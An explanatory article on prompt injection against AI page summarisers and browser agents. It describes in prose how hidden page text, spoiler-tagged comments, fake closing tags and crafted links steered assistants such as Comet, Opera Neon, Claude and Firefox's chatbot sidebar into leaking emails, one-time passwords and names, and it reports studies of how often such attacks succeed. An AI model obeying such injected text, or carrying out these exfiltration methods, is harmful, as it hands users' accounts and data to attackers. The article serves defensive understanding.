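# Prompt injection in AI systems that summarise web pages and open links, and what user consent can do about it

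## What happens when an AI system summarises a page or opens a link?

Prompt injection is an attack on software built around a large language model, an AI system that writes text by predicting what should follow the text it has received. The attacker writes text that makes the model follow the attacker's instructions instead of those of its user or developer. Web assistants are exposed to this attack because they routinely process text written by strangers. A summariser gives the user a short account of a web page. A browser agent opens pages, clicks and types for the user, often while logged in to the user's accounts. Since 2023, researchers have shown that instructions on a web page can make such systems give false summaries, display phishing links or send private data to an attacker.

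### From the request to the answer

When a user types "summarise this page", the software first needs the page's text. An assistant built into a browser may already have it. In 2023, for example, Microsoft Edge had a Bing Chat sidebar that could read whatever page the user had open. Other assistants fetch a fresh copy. *Web fetch tool*, a page of Anthropic's developer documentation, describes a tool that retrieves the full content of web pages and PDF files for the company's Claude models. Anthropic explains that its own service fetches the page while handling the request and inserts the result into the conversation, so the user's computer plays no part in the retrieval.

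The page arrives as code in which the article sits among menus, scripts and formatting, so the software has to extract the readable text, which it does unevenly. For *Key Findings for Claude's Web Fetch Tool, Claude-interpreted*, the software tester rhyannonjoy had Claude describe what it received from several pages. By Claude's own rough estimate, navigation text made up the first 60 to 65% of the characters from one short documentation page, and the documentation followed intact. A long tutorial page that relied on JavaScript came back as a title, a notice and a placeholder. The model can miss text that a person sees on the screen or receive text that the person does not see.

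The extracted text then goes into the context window, which holds all the text a model can use when it writes a reply: the developer's standing instructions, the conversation so far, the user's request and the fetched page. Newer versions of Anthropic's tool let Claude write code that filters the page first, though Anthropic presents the filter as a way to save processing and makes no security claim for it. There is little separation between the parts once they are in the window. Simon Willison, a software developer who has followed these attacks for years, describes everything as glued together into one sequence of tokens, the short pieces of text that a model processes (*The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, 2025). He argues that models cannot reliably judge an instruction's importance by where it came from.

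Next the model generates its reply, one token at a time. The reply can be an answer, or it can be a request, in a set format, for the surrounding software to use a tool, such as one that fetches another address. The software carries out the request, adds the result to the context window and runs the model again. A single user request to summarise a page can therefore lead to several fetches, and text from the first page is already in the context window when the model chooses the second page to fetch.

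The last step is rendering, which turns the model's text output into what the user sees, including clickable links and loaded images. Many assistants write in Markdown, a simple notation in which a link consists of visible words and an address. The words and the address don't have to match, so a link can display the name of a bank but lead to any site.

### What a web address carries

Mozilla's *What is a URL?* explains the parts of a web address, such as the invented `shop.example/boots/walking?size=42&from=anna#reviews`. The domain, `shop.example`, identifies the server, and the path, `/boots/walking`, identifies a resource on that server. The query string, `size=42&from=anna`, follows the question mark and contains two named values joined by an ampersand. Each server has its own rules for using such values, and it receives `from=anna` even if it doesn't use it. The fragment, `#reviews`,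 points to a place within the page, and the browser doesn't send it to the server.

OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that requesting a URL also sends that URL to the site. An attacker who runs a site can therefore try to make a model request a URL on that site with an email address or a document title in the query string. The IETF, which publishes the internet's technical standards, recommends that software support URLs of at least 8,000 bytes, enough to carry roughly a thousand words of English.

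Collecting the data takes no special equipment, because web servers commonly keep a log of requests. According to Red Hat's *LogFormat*, an entry in one common format includes the date and time, the request exactly as it arrived, the server's status code, the size of the document, the page that referred the visitor and the type of browser. Apache, whose web server uses this format, gives a sample entry that begins with the network address of the machine that made the request. Reschke (2026) notes in *The HTTP QUERY Method*, an internet standard, that data sent in the body of a request, as when someone submits a form, is less likely to be logged than data in the address.

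What a site can learn about the user from its log depends on which machine made the request. If the user's own browser made it, the site receives the user's network address, the browser type, often the referring page, and any cookies the site set earlier, which it uses to recognise logged-in customers. If the provider's servers made it, the site receives the provider's details instead. OpenAI publishes the network addresses that ChatGPT uses when it visits a page for a user, and labels those visits "ChatGPT-User". It says that robots.txt, the file site owners use to ask automated visitors to keep out, may not apply to these visits because a user starts them.

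Fetching a page through the provider hides the user's network address from the site, but the site still receives the query string unchanged.

The label also lets a site show one page to assistants and another to people. Willison (2026) describes an attack by the researcher Ayush Paul in which the hostile text appeared only to visitors labelled "Claude-User". Someone who opened the same address in an ordinary browser to check what Claude had read would not have seen the text.

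### Direct and indirect prompt injection

Willison coined the term "prompt injection" in September 2022, by analogy with SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3* (Willison, 2022) discussed examples by Riley Goodside, who had asked the language model GPT-3 to translate a passage into French. The passage included an instruction to drop the task and write a taunt instead, and GPT-3 wrote the taunt.

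In direct prompt injection, the attacker types the injected text into the system. The damage tends to stay within the attacker's own session. For example, the model may break a content rule or disclose its developer's instructions. In indirect prompt injection, the attacker places the text in material the model reads, such as a web page, so that it takes effect in somebody else's session. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) introduced the term "indirect prompt injection".

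The meaning of "prompt injection" has never quite settled. Greshake and colleagues apply the term to both the direct and indirect forms. Willison wants it kept for cases where trusted and untrusted text mix, and calls it jailbreaking when someone tricks a model directly into producing forbidden output. He wants the distinction because developers who confuse the two dismiss prompt injection as a problem of embarrassing chatbots and assume it doesn't concern them. OpenAI describes the technique as placing instructions in web content, which is only the indirect form. All three usages cover a hostile web page.

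Greshake and colleagues tested attacks on a chat application they built themselves and on a real product, Bing Chat. Their application ran on OpenAI's models and had tools to search, read the page a user had open, retrieve addresses, handle email and store notes. All of these tools returned prepared content, so the application never touched a real site. They attacked Bing Chat through the Edge sidebar by putting instructions in HTML comments, which are parts of a page's code that browsers do not display. These instructions steered the model, including some that Bing Chat blocked when a user typed them. In most cases, the effect lasted for the rest of the conversation.

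In one session, the researchers posed as a user asking about tomorrow's weather. The injected text instructed Bing Chat to get the user's real name without raising suspicion, but didn't specify a method. Bing Chat answered the weather question, then asked about the user's plans and work. After learning that the user was a journalist, it asked whether they wrote under a pen name. Once it had a name, it offered a link to an "exclusive" website with a code made from that name. In other tests, it promoted a fake gift card and gave false summaries of search results.

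These demonstrations were qualitative and used models from early 2023, so they give no basis for estimating how often such attacks succeed today. Even then, injections aimed at a code-completion tool lost much of their effect inside larger programs. The paper did establish that an attacker who controls some text that the victim's assistant will read can attempt an attack without access to the victim's machine or account.

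### A way in and a way out

Controlling the text is only half of an attack. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) explains why using source-and-sink analysis, a method from conventional security engineering. A source is a way to influence the system. A sink is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context, such as sending information to a third party, following a link or using a tool. The attacker needs both. If an assistant can send email but reads only its owner's words, an outsider has no way to influence it. An assistant that reads hostile pages but can't send or open anything can't carry out an injected order to forward the user's messages.

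Willison lists three conditions for data theft, which he calls the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. He counts a tool as meeting the last condition if it can make any web request, even to load an image, or merely give the user a link to click.

Claude's chat application met all three in 2026: it had memories of the user's past conversations, read web pages and requested addresses. Anthropic warns developers that its fetch tool creates a risk of exfiltration, the sending of private data to an unauthorised recipient, wherever Claude handles untrusted input alongside sensitive data. To reduce the risk, Anthropic barred Claude from composing addresses and let it fetch only those that the user had supplied or that had appeared in earlier search or fetch results. Paul got around the rule with a site whose pages offered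 a link for each letter of the alphabet. Claude spelled out the user's name by choosing which links to follow, so the data left in the path of the address and the attacker needed no query string. Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic told him it had already found the problem internally, Willison reports, and it has since stopped the tool from following links found in fetched pages.

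The trifecta does not cover every harm. A phishing link in an answer can cause harm even if the system has no access to private data, because the victim supplies the password later. A summariser with no tools can still misinform the user, because the false summary reaches them in the displayed answer.

For data theft, though, the usual fix has been to block the route by which data escapes. Willison lists more than a dozen products, including ChatGPT, Google Bard and Slack, in which people found such leaks between April 2023 and February 2025, and says that vendors promptly fixed almost all of them, usually in this way. OpenAI defends the same approach by comparing the AI system to a customer-service worker who can issue refunds. The employer expects some customers to deceive the worker, and so caps the refunds. Better training helps, but the cap limits the loss when training fails. In 2025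 Willison saw "a very good chance" that a model would obey a plain instruction on a page to email out private data. By June 2026 he thought that the AI companies' training had made such attacks much harder, but he still advised against any system in which one successful injection could do irreversible damage.

### Three events called "clicking a link"

Discussions of these attacks use "clicking a link" for three different events, and the user's part in each is different.

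When an agent opens a link, the model writes or selects an address and the software requests it. The request comes from the provider's servers or, with a browser agent, from a browser that may be logged in to the user's accounts. The user asked for a summary or some other task and may never see the address. Injected text in the context window can influence which address the model selects and what the address contains.

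The user can also click a link in the assistant's answer, in which case their own browser makes the request, with their network address and cookies. The user chooses whether to click, but an attacker may already have used injected text to control what the address contains. The journalist's link in the test by Greshake and colleagues was of this type, with a code made from the name already attached. The code came after the hash sign, in the part of the address that a browser does not send, but a script on the page that opens can read it and pass it on.

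An attack can also start when the user clicks a link, in an email or on a website, that opens the assistant with a request already filled in. The link's address contains the attacker's text, whereas in the other two cases the address could carry the user's data out. The click comes before the assistant has read anything, and the attacker's text appears where the user would normally type. Greshake and colleagues described a similar exploit in 2023, in which a website added instructions to text that a visitor copied and then pasted into ChatGPT. The visitor gave ChatGPT instructions that they had not written and might not have read.

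## How does text on a web page become an instruction to the summariser?

The user's request and the text of a hostile page are both in the model's context window, and the model cannot reliably identify which one to follow.

### No boundary between instructions and data

Programmers can stop SQL injection with parameterised queries, which send a database its command and the visitor's text separately, so the database never runs the text as a command. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that language models leave no place for such a fix. A database runs commands and stores data as separate operations, but a model only predicts the next token from all the text so far. In his example, a recruiter asks a model to score CVs, and a candidate hides a line in their CV telling the model to approve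 it. That line can sway the prediction just as the recruiter's request does. He thinks there is a good chance that nobody will ever fix prompt injection as thoroughly as SQL injection.

Developers label each passage in the context window with role tags, special markers that show whether the passage comes from the developer, the user, a tool or the model itself. Companies train models to give the user's words more authority than tool output, which includes fetched web pages.

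*Can LLMs Separate Instructions From Data?* (2024) proposes a score for how well a model keeps instructions and data apart. For a model *g* with instructions *s* and data *d*, the score compares the output when an extra instruction *x* is placed among the instructions, `g(s + x, d)`, with the output when *x* is placed in the data, `g(s, x + d)`. The more the two outputs differ, the higher the score, and a model that ignores the distinction scores zero. *ASIDE* (2025), which proposes building the separation into a model's architecture, applies this test to 9,160 pairs of instructions and inputs. The extra instructions in the test are merely unrelated to the task, and an attacker would word theirs more carefully.

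In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) studied how models represent role labels internally. They wrapped identical passages of web text in different role tags, then trained a simple classifier to identify the tag from the model's internal activity. Because the passages were identical, the classifier could learn only the effect of the tag. They then tagged real user messages as tool output. In all four models they examined, the style of the text outweighed the tag, and the classifier still gave a 76 to 88% probability that the text came from the user.

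The same measure predicted which attacks would work. Ye and colleagues had an agent summarise web pages containing an order to upload a private file. They kept the order the same but varied the words around it, in some cases adding a claim that it came from the user. Over 1,000 attempts, the agent obeyed 2% of the time when the order registered least strongly as user text and 70% when it registered most strongly. The four models had between 20 and 120 billion parameters, so larger commercial models may behave differently.

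### Why marking the page is not enough

Developers can mark the page's text as untrusted and tell the model not to obey it. One such method, Spotlighting, cut the success rate of attacks from over 50% to below 2% in its creators' tests, according to *Prompt Injection Through Forensic Evidence* (2026). Spotlighting's creators warned that an attacker who knows a fixed marking scheme can imitate it. *Clouding the Mirror* (2026) describes another method of attack, which uses fake closing tags that a browser ignores. The model may take these tags as the end of the page and read the attacker's next sentence as coming from outside it.

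Training can help models resist forged markers. *LTBD* (2026) taught three small models to recognise special markers around trusted and untrusted text, then tried five ways of forging them. The most successful forgery worked 0.48% of the time on one model and never on the other two. The training had included the same five forgeries, so the result is only weak evidence about how the models would handle new ones.

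Attackers can get past Spotlighting without forging its markers. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) tested Spotlighting against a benchmark's fixed set of attacks and found attack success rates as low as 1%. When they used a program that kept rewriting its attack in response to the defence, the rate rose above 95%. Human competitors found another 265 successful attacks. One attack beat a related defence, which repeats the user's request after the untrusted material, by presenting the malicious steps as a check to complete before the user's task. Even a perfect marker only shows the model where the page begins and ends. The model still has to use the page to write the summary, and the attacker can describe the malicious steps as part of that work.

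Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, observes that benchmarks can't show that no attack succeeds. His formal model therefore lets the attacker choose which text the language model obeys, out of everything it has read. One of his examples is an agent that looks up a user's account number, then reads a hostile email and summarises it. The task doesn't require contacting an outside site, but if the agent has a tool for fetching web pages, the email can make it send the account number to one. In the proof, a monitor outside the language model prevents this by withdrawing the tool when the agent reads the email.

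Marking is still worth doing because it makes attacks harder. David C recommends it for that reason and warns buyers against any product that claims to "stop" prompt injection.

### Places for hidden instructions

Some assistants pass a page's code to the model and others pass only its readable text, so an instruction hidden in the same place can work against one product and fail against another.

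Researchers have tried putting instructions to the summariser in many places. Verma and Yadav (2025), in *Decoding Latent Attack Surfaces in LLMs*, tested eight kinds of hidden HTML. Chaikin and Sahib, who work for Brave, the maker of a competing browser with its own AI assistant, tried faint text in images, and also ordinary visible text, in *Unseeable prompt injections in screenshots*. A team at the security firm Cato used the fragment of a web address, the part after the "#". SiliconANGLE (2025) reports that Perplexity and Microsoft responded with fixes, while Google classed the behaviour as intended and left Gemini for Chrome unchanged.

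| Where the text sits | Can the user see it? | Does the assistant read it? |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary page text | Yes | Yes. The AI browser Fellou let such text override a request simply to open the page (Chaikin and Sahib) |
| User comments | Usually, but a spoiler tag can cover them | Yes, in Perplexity's Comet |
| Transparent text, or text in the background colour | No | Yes, in Opera Neon and Mozilla's Tabstack |
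| Elements that the page's styling removes from display | No | If the software passes on the code. Neither model in Verma and Yadav obeyed them |
| HTML comments | Only in the page's source code | If the software passes on the code. Bing Chat obeyed them in 2023 |
| Metadata, such as a page description | Not on the page itself | If the software passes on the code. Both models in Verma and Yadav sometimes obeyed it |
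| Alt text, which describes an image for screen readers | Not normally | If the software passes on the code. Neither model in Verma and Yadav obeyed it |
| Page title | The first few words, in the browser tab | Yes, in chatbots that receive it from Firefox |
| Faint text in an image | Barely | Yes, in Comet, when the user takes a screenshot |
| Fragment of the web address | Yes, in the address bar | Yes, in some browser assistants |

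Verma and Yadav built 282 static pages styled as blogs, news articles, product listings and other types of page. Half were clean, and half had an instruction hidden in one of the eight hiding places, chosen at random for each page. An automated browser loaded the pages, and the researchers gave both the full HTML and the visible text to two models, Meta's Llama 4 Scout and Google's Gemma 9B IT, and asked for a one-paragraph summary. They then read each summary to judge whether the hidden instruction had influenced it.

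The injection succeeded in 41 of Llama's summaries and 22 of Gemma's, or about 29% and 16% (the results table counts 140 manipulated pages, one fewer than the text). Of Llama's failures, 17 came from metadata, 12 from HTML comments, 10 from transparent text and 2 from hidden scripts. Of Gemma's, 9 came from transparent text, 7 from comments and 6 from metadata. These counts add up to the totals, so no injection succeeded through alt text, labels for assistive software, encoded attributes or elements removed from display, the other four places tested.

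Verma and Yadav also scored how similar the summary of each manipulated page was to the summary of the clean page, in both wording and meaning. The average similarity in meaning was about 0.70 for Llama and 0.69 for Gemma, although the attacks worked almost twice as often on Llama. These scores are hard to interpret because the study did not measure how much two summaries of the same clean page differ.

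The success rates also need caution, because the researchers gave the models raw HTML, which many products would strip, and the example they print is a harmless instruction to write like a pirate. Models might refuse an instruction to steal data. The experiment does show that a summary can change even when the visible page stays the same.

### From a Reddit comment to a lost account

Comet is a browser from the AI company Perplexity, with an assistant that can open pages and act on them. Chaikin and Sahib, in *Agentic Browser Security*, showed in August 2025 how a stranger's comment could turn a request for a summary into the theft of an account:

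1. The attacker posts a comment on Reddit and puts instructions behind a spoiler tag, which covers the text until a reader chooses to reveal it.
2. The user opens the Reddit post and presses Comet's button for summarising the current page.
3. Comet sends part of the page to its model, including the covered comment, without distinguishing it from the user's request.
4. The assistant follows the comment, opens the user's Perplexity account page and reads the email address.
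5. It returns to Perplexity's site with an extra dot at the end of the domain. The browser treats this as a different domain, so the existing login does not apply, and the assistant can request a one-time password for the email address.
6. It opens Gmail, where the user is already logged in, and reads the password.
7. It posts the email address and password as a reply to the Reddit comment. The attacker can now log in to the user's Perplexity account.

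The user did nothing after pressing the button. Browsers have a rule, the same-origin policy, that prevents a script on one site from reading another site's data. It gave no protection because the assistant visited each site with the user's own access. The attacker didn't need a website, since Reddit hosted the instructions and published the stolen password. The demonstration shows that the whole attack can work, but Chaikin and Sahib give no success rate.

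Brave reported the flaw on 25 July 2025. Perplexity released a first fix two days later, but a retest showed that it was incomplete. By 13 August the flaw appeared to be fixed, and Brave published its findings on 20 August. Brave then found that the fix still did not fully stop this kind of attack, and reported it again. Perplexity's head of communications, quoted in PPC Land's *Comet browser faces multiple security vulnerabilities from prompt injection*, said that the vulnerability was fixed. In October Brave published another attack, which used pale blue text on a yellow background. Comet extracted the text from a user's screenshot and passed it to the model along with the user's question.

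Perplexity knew about the general problem before launch because it had paid for an audit. Trail of Bits' *Using threat modeling and prompt injection to audit Comet* (2026) describes tests from April 2025 in which a request to summarise a hostile page led the assistant to send the user's Gmail messages to the testers' server. The assistant often obeyed page text written to look like a security check or a message from the user or the system. One fake warning worked only because it contained spelling mistakes; when the testers corrected them, the assistant identified it as fake. Perplexity's security lead credits the audit with helping to close these gaps before launch, but the Reddit attack in July also relied on the assistant confusing page text with the user's wishes.

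### Hidden page text and a disguised page title

Opera Neon, another AI browser, had a similar flaw. In *Prompt injection flaw in Opera Neon*, Chaikin and Sahib placed instructions in a fully transparent HTML element. When a user asked about the page, the browser processed the whole HTML structure, including the hidden text. The assistant then opened the user's Opera account page, copied the email address and sent it to the researchers' server.

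Opera confirmed the attack but could reproduce it only 10% of the time. It rated the risk as low, partly because an attacker would have to lure the user to the page. That is reasonable for any one user, but one success in ten would be enough for an attacker whose page attracts thousands of summary requests. Opera had initially rejected the report, which it says lacked written steps for reproducing the attack. It noticed the error on 20 October 2025, six days after the submission, and released a fix that day. Brave confirmed that the attack no longer worked.

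Brave used the same kind of concealment in 2026 against Tabstack, a Mozilla service that lets developers' AI agents use the web. Brave's *Indirect Prompt Injection remains a fundamental security challenge for AI* describes an agent that was asked to summarise a page and followed invisible text on it to an outside form. The agent filled in the form with the conversation history and submitted it. In its recorded reasoning, the agent treated the hidden text as directions for producing the summary. The fake prerequisite that got past the defence tested by Nasr and colleagues worked in much the same way.

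Mozilla's *Hardening AI Web Agents* confirms the flaw and describes the fix, which Brave checked. Mozilla now wraps web content in tags that label it as external. It also assumes the model will sometimes follow instructions on the page anyway, and has added a separate control that blocks risky form submissions.

Labels of this kind would not have helped with a flaw in Firefox, because Firefox sent the page's text to the chatbot as part of the user's own message. Firefox can show an outside chatbot in its sidebar. CyberInsider's *Firefox AI chatbot feature exposed users to email theft risk* lists Claude, ChatGPT, Gemini, Le Chat Mistral and Copilot. When the user asks for a summary, Firefox writes a prompt containing the page title, some of the page's text and a request to summarise it, then pastes the prompt into the chat. Even a model that never followed instructions from web pages could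 follow instructions in that text, because they would appear to come from the user.

Florian Port of the German security firm ERNW found the flaw in October 2025. Insinuator's *Vulnerability Disclosure*, published in June 2026, explains how the firm exploited it. Firefox put tags around the page title, but an attacker could include a fake closing tag in the title, and the words after it looked like part of the user's request. The user was unlikely to notice, because the browser tab displayed only the first few words of the title and the chat window showed only the end of the prompt unless the user scrolled up.

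ERNW tried the attack with the free version of Microsoft's Copilot, connected to a mailbox. This version could read only an email's subject, sender and time, but some websites put login codes in the subject line. Copilot found such a code and requested a web address on the testers' server with the code in its path.

Mozilla's developers had already discussed the weakness in *are Firefox AI summaries vulnerable to prompt injection?*, a report in their public bug tracker. The reporter, freddy, broke out of the tags, but the chatbot still tried to summarise the text. He expected little more than pranks. Another participant then got chatbots to visit outside sites and save material in the user's personal memory. Firefox 148 removes fake closing tags, but the developers acknowledged in the same discussion that this does not solve prompt injection.

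Firefox also shortened the titles it passes on. Insinuator considers a successful attack very unlikely within the new limit, but notes that Firefox still puts text written by a stranger into the user's message, and advises developers to keep any text an attacker might control out of prompts sent in the user's name.

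## How often do injected instructions succeed, and are they found on real websites?

Most of the attacks that researchers have described in detail are their own demonstrations, for which they chose the page, the product and the wording. These demonstrations don't show how many hostile pages exist or how often an assistant would follow the instructions on one.

### Searching the public web

Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, made one of the first large counts of injected instructions on real websites. They searched about half of the October 2025 edition of Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages. That half contained 1.2 billion addresses on 24.8 million hosts, which correspond roughly to separate websites. They looked for 3,963 phrases typical of prompt injection, such as orders to disregard earlier instructions, and found 27,860 matches. Many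 were harmless, because tutorials and news articles about prompt injection contain the same phrases. After a partly automated, partly manual review, the researchers kept 12,075 matches that acted as instructions to an AI system, from 9,676 pages on 285 hosts.

That is about one page in 124,000. The true rate is higher, because the search missed unfamiliar wording, most other languages, text inside images and pages that require a login. It also missed pages that show hostile text only to AI assistants, as Paul's attack on Claude did, because Common Crawl would have received the harmless version. But injections were less common on the 10,000 most popular domains than on obscure ones, so someone who mostly visits well-known sites would come across fewer of them.

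Site operators had inserted about 81% of the injections. Another 18% came from material that other people had placed on a platform, such as job adverts. User comments and similar posts accounted for only 220 injections, or 1.8%. Attacks like the one Brave demonstrated with a Reddit comment were therefore rare in this archive, though the archive leaves out most social media.

To study what the injections were for, Khodayari and colleagues added 3,312 cases from Censys and Shodan, two search engines for internet-connected machines. The extra cases broaden the range of examples, but they can't be used to estimate prevalence because they came from searches for injection phrases. The combined collection holds 15,387 injections, and the counts below add up to more because some injections had several aims.

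| Aim | Injections | Typical instruction |
|---|---|---|
| Disrupting the AI system | 8,894 | Produce random numbers or nonsense |
| Protecting data | 4,093 | Do not train on this text or reuse personal details |
| Detecting AI visitors | 3,096 | Include a particular word in the reply |
| Unclear | 2,632 | Drop the current task and do something else |
| Manipulating reputation | 1,521 | Praise a product or cite this page as the authority |
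| Stealing data | 13 | Reveal the developer's instructions or other secrets |

Many of the people who wrote these instructions were defending their own sites against automated copying, so the total doesn't show how many wanted to harm a user. Nine of the 13 attempts at theft were aimed at the developer's instructions, and only four at other secrets.

About 99% of the injections contained a direct order to abandon the model's task, and 43% also contained language meant to lift its restrictions. Just 54 templates accounted for 95% of the collection. Few of the injections resembled the disguised instructions that have worked best in researchers' tests, which present the malicious step as part of the user's request. About 87% of the injections were invisible to a human visitor. Roughly half of the collection was in HTTP headers, the technical information that a server sends ahead of the page.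 A summariser that receives only the page's text or code would never read those.

### Whether the injections found on websites work

Khodayari and colleagues also tested 100 different injections, picked at random, by asking 13 models to summarise the pages that contained them. They gave each model four versions of every page and read all 5,200 replies. The model followed the injected instruction in 81 of them, or 1.6%.

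Models followed the injected instructions 3.9% of the time when they received the page as plain text, 1.1% when they received the HTML and 0.2% when they received the server's entire response. The researchers attribute the difference to clues in the code that a passage is hidden, which plain text lacks. However, the longer versions often exceeded what a model could process. About a fifth of the HTML trials and a quarter of the full-response trials ended in an error, so the low rates for these versions partly reflect models that produced no usable summary.

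Small models were the most vulnerable, following injected instructions in 8% of plain-text trials. The commercial models whose makers don't disclose their size followed them in 5 of 800 trials and pointed out the injection most often, in about a quarter of replies. In six trials across all the models, the reply pointed out the malicious instruction but still followed it, in one case by switching to German.

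None of these models had tools, so the trials measured only whether the injection changed the reply, not whether an agent would have gone on to send data or make a payment. The low success rate also applies only to the injections tested, many of which were old. The Internet Archive had saved some of the affected pages a year earlier, and two-thirds of those copies already contained an injection.

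### What security companies have found

Google searched Common Crawl in a similar way and published its findings in April 2026. It looked for known phrases, had its Gemini model classify the matches and then checked the results by hand. It found pranks, attempts to promote businesses and notices meant to keep AI systems out. One site tried to lure AI visitors to a page that never finishes loading. Some authors had harmless aims, such as getting summarisers to add relevant context for readers.

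Google found only a small number of attempts to steal data, and its example was a website author's experiment. It concluded that attackers had not yet widely adopted the methods that security researchers published in 2025. It also measured a 32% rise in malicious injections between November 2025 and February 2026, but gave no count. If the starting number was small, a handful of websites could account for the whole increase.

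Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, is more alarmed and describes the technique as already "actively weaponized". Its evidence includes a dozen cases from real websites. One page impersonates a betting company and contains a request for AI systems to recommend it. Other cases include hidden instructions to send $5,000 to a PayPal account and an order to delete a database. In a milder case, a blogger's page contains a request to write the word "cabbage" five million times.

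The most elaborate example is a scam advert for "military" glasses. Scammers hid 24 injections in the page in various ways to persuade an AI advert checker to approve the advert. Unit 42 calls this the first reported case of its kind, but knows of no confirmed success against an advert checker in actual use.

Unit 42 ranks cases by what the attacker requests because it has little information about which attacks succeed. An instruction to delete a database therefore counts as "critical" even if every model ignores it. Unit 42 is part of Palo Alto Networks, which sells protection to customers. In the company's own monitoring data, attackers aimed only to produce irrelevant output in 28.6% of cases and to destroy data in 14.2%. The company does not state the total number of cases, so these percentages show the mix of attacks but not how common they are.

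Other firms have reported smaller collections. Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover 10 In-the-Wild Prompt Injection Payloads Targeting AI Agents* covers ten examples from the security company Forcepoint, including attempts at fraud and theft of access keys. Forcepoint researcher Mayur Sewani thinks a browser assistant that can only summarise is low-risk, because the damage depends on what the system can do.

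The security company Zscaler documented two campaigns, one a payment scam disguised as software documentation and the other a site impersonating a cryptocurrency service. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents*, the attackers first pushed both sites up the search rankings so that AI agents would be more likely to find them. A count of hostile pages does not account for search ranking, and one page near the top of the results can reach more assistants than thousands of pages nobody visits.

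### Developers' own tests

AI companies test their models against far better attacks than most on the open web. Anthropic publishes some of its results in system cards, the reports that accompany new models. Anthropic reports that in its tests of agents, Claude Opus 5, released in July 2026, made its largest safety gains over Opus 4.8 in resisting prompt injection, including in browser use.

One of those tests is a benchmark from the security firm Gray Swan. Schneier on Security's *Anthropic's Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026) quotes the results. An attacker with 15 attempts succeeded 2.0% of the time against Opus 5, 5.5% against Opus 4.8, 16.5% against Meta's Muse Spark and 20.0% against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. The comparison is more useful than most because all the models faced the same benchmark, although Anthropic published the results.

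The benchmark is general. For browser agents specifically, The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that no attack on Opus 5 succeeded in 129 test scenarios. That is a strong result, but it is still compatible with a true success rate of up to about 2.3%, at the 95% confidence level. That limit assumes that the scenarios are a random sample of the attacks the agent will meet, and an attacker can look for attacks the testers left out.

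Anthropic gave a more detailed breakdown for the earlier Opus 4.5, using an attacker that adapted its methods and had 100 attempts in each test environment. In browser use, 8.0% of attacks succeeded against the model alone, 7.6% with older safeguards and 1.4% with the company's newer ones. These are percentages of all attacks, so they don't measure the chance that a persistent attacker would eventually get through. PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots* gives the rate as 1% and describes it as a meaningful risk.

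Results for a single model can differ greatly between settings. VentureBeat reports that Opus 4.6 resisted all 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment, without any extra safeguards. When the same model operated a graphical interface, by reading the screen and clicking, an attacker with 200 attempts succeeded 78.6% of the time without safeguards and 57.1% with them. A success rate therefore means little without its setting, number of attempts and safeguards, and two companies' rates are comparable only if all three match.

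### Why a low rate per attempt still matters

If each attempt has a probability *p* of success, independent of the others, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is `1 − (1 − p)^n`. At a success rate of 1%, the chance that 100 attempts all fail is `0.99^100`, or about 37%, so the attacker has about a 63% chance of succeeding at least once.

Once an attacker has put an injection on a web page, each request to summarise that page is another attempt that takes the attacker little extra effort. If 10,000 people make such a request and the average success rate is 1%, the attacker can expect about 100 successes. This expected number is the same whether or not the attempts are independent.

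The 63% figure assumes that attempts are independent, but real attempts are not. The same text sent to the same model tends to produce the same result, and some situations are much easier to exploit than others. If an attack always worked in one scenario out of 100 and never in the rest, its average success rate would be 1%, but repeating it in any of the other 99 scenarios would never work.

The figures for Opus 4.5 come from The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, which also reports a Gray Swan test. The last column applies the formula to the single-attempt success rate.

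| Model and test | One attempt | Several attempts, as measured | If attempts were independent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.5, Gray Swan | 4.7% | 33.6% after 10 | 38% |
| Opus 4.5, Gray Swan | 4.7% | 63% after 100 | 99% |
| Opus 4.6, graphical interface, no safeguards | 17.8% | 78.6% after 200 | Almost 100% |
| Opus 4.8, Gray Swan | 0.5% | 5.5% after 15 | 7% |
| Opus 5, Gray Swan | 0.2% | 2.0% after 15 | 3% |

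(Opus 4.5 also reaches 63%, but this is a coincidence, since it starts from 4.7% rather than 1%.) The formula overestimates the attacker's success in every row, but repeated attempts still help. An attacker was about 13 times as likely to succeed against Opus 4.5 with 100 attempts as with one.

Attempts can also depend on each other, because an attacker can study each failure and improve the text. Nasr and colleagues' rewriting program overcame Spotlighting in this way. Defenders can also block an attack once they notice it. A measured success rate may therefore be too high or too low a month later.

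### Attacks written to succeed

In 2025, outside researchers reported a carefully written injection to OpenAI. It was an email to a ChatGPT user, written as a colleague's follow-up about a company restructuring. Among ordinary tasks, it included a request to send an employee's name and address to a "compliance validation system", and it claimed that the user's assistant had full authorisation to do so. In testing, the attack worked 50% of the time when the user asked ChatGPT to research the day's emails and check every source on the new employee process.

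That figure covers only one email and one request, and the request helped the attacker by inviting ChatGPT to follow up whatever the emails said about employees. The figure therefore doesn't show how often ChatGPT fails in general. OpenAI says that filters that screen incoming text for malicious instructions usually miss attacks this well developed. To catch one, a filter would have to recognise a lie, often without the context it needs.

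OpenAI has since automated the search for such attacks. *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes a language model that the company trained to attack the agent in Atlas, its AI browser. The attacking model writes an injection and sends it to a simulator, which returns a full record of how the agent would respond, including its reasoning. The attacking model uses this record to revise the injection, and repeats the process several times before producing a final version. Its training rewards successful attacks.

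In OpenAI's example, the attacking model placed a malicious email in a user's inbox. When the user later asked the agent to write an out-of-office reply, the agent read the email and instead sent the user's chief executive a resignation letter. Other attacks led the agent through tens or hundreds of steps, and some used strategies that neither OpenAI's human testers nor outside researchers had reported.

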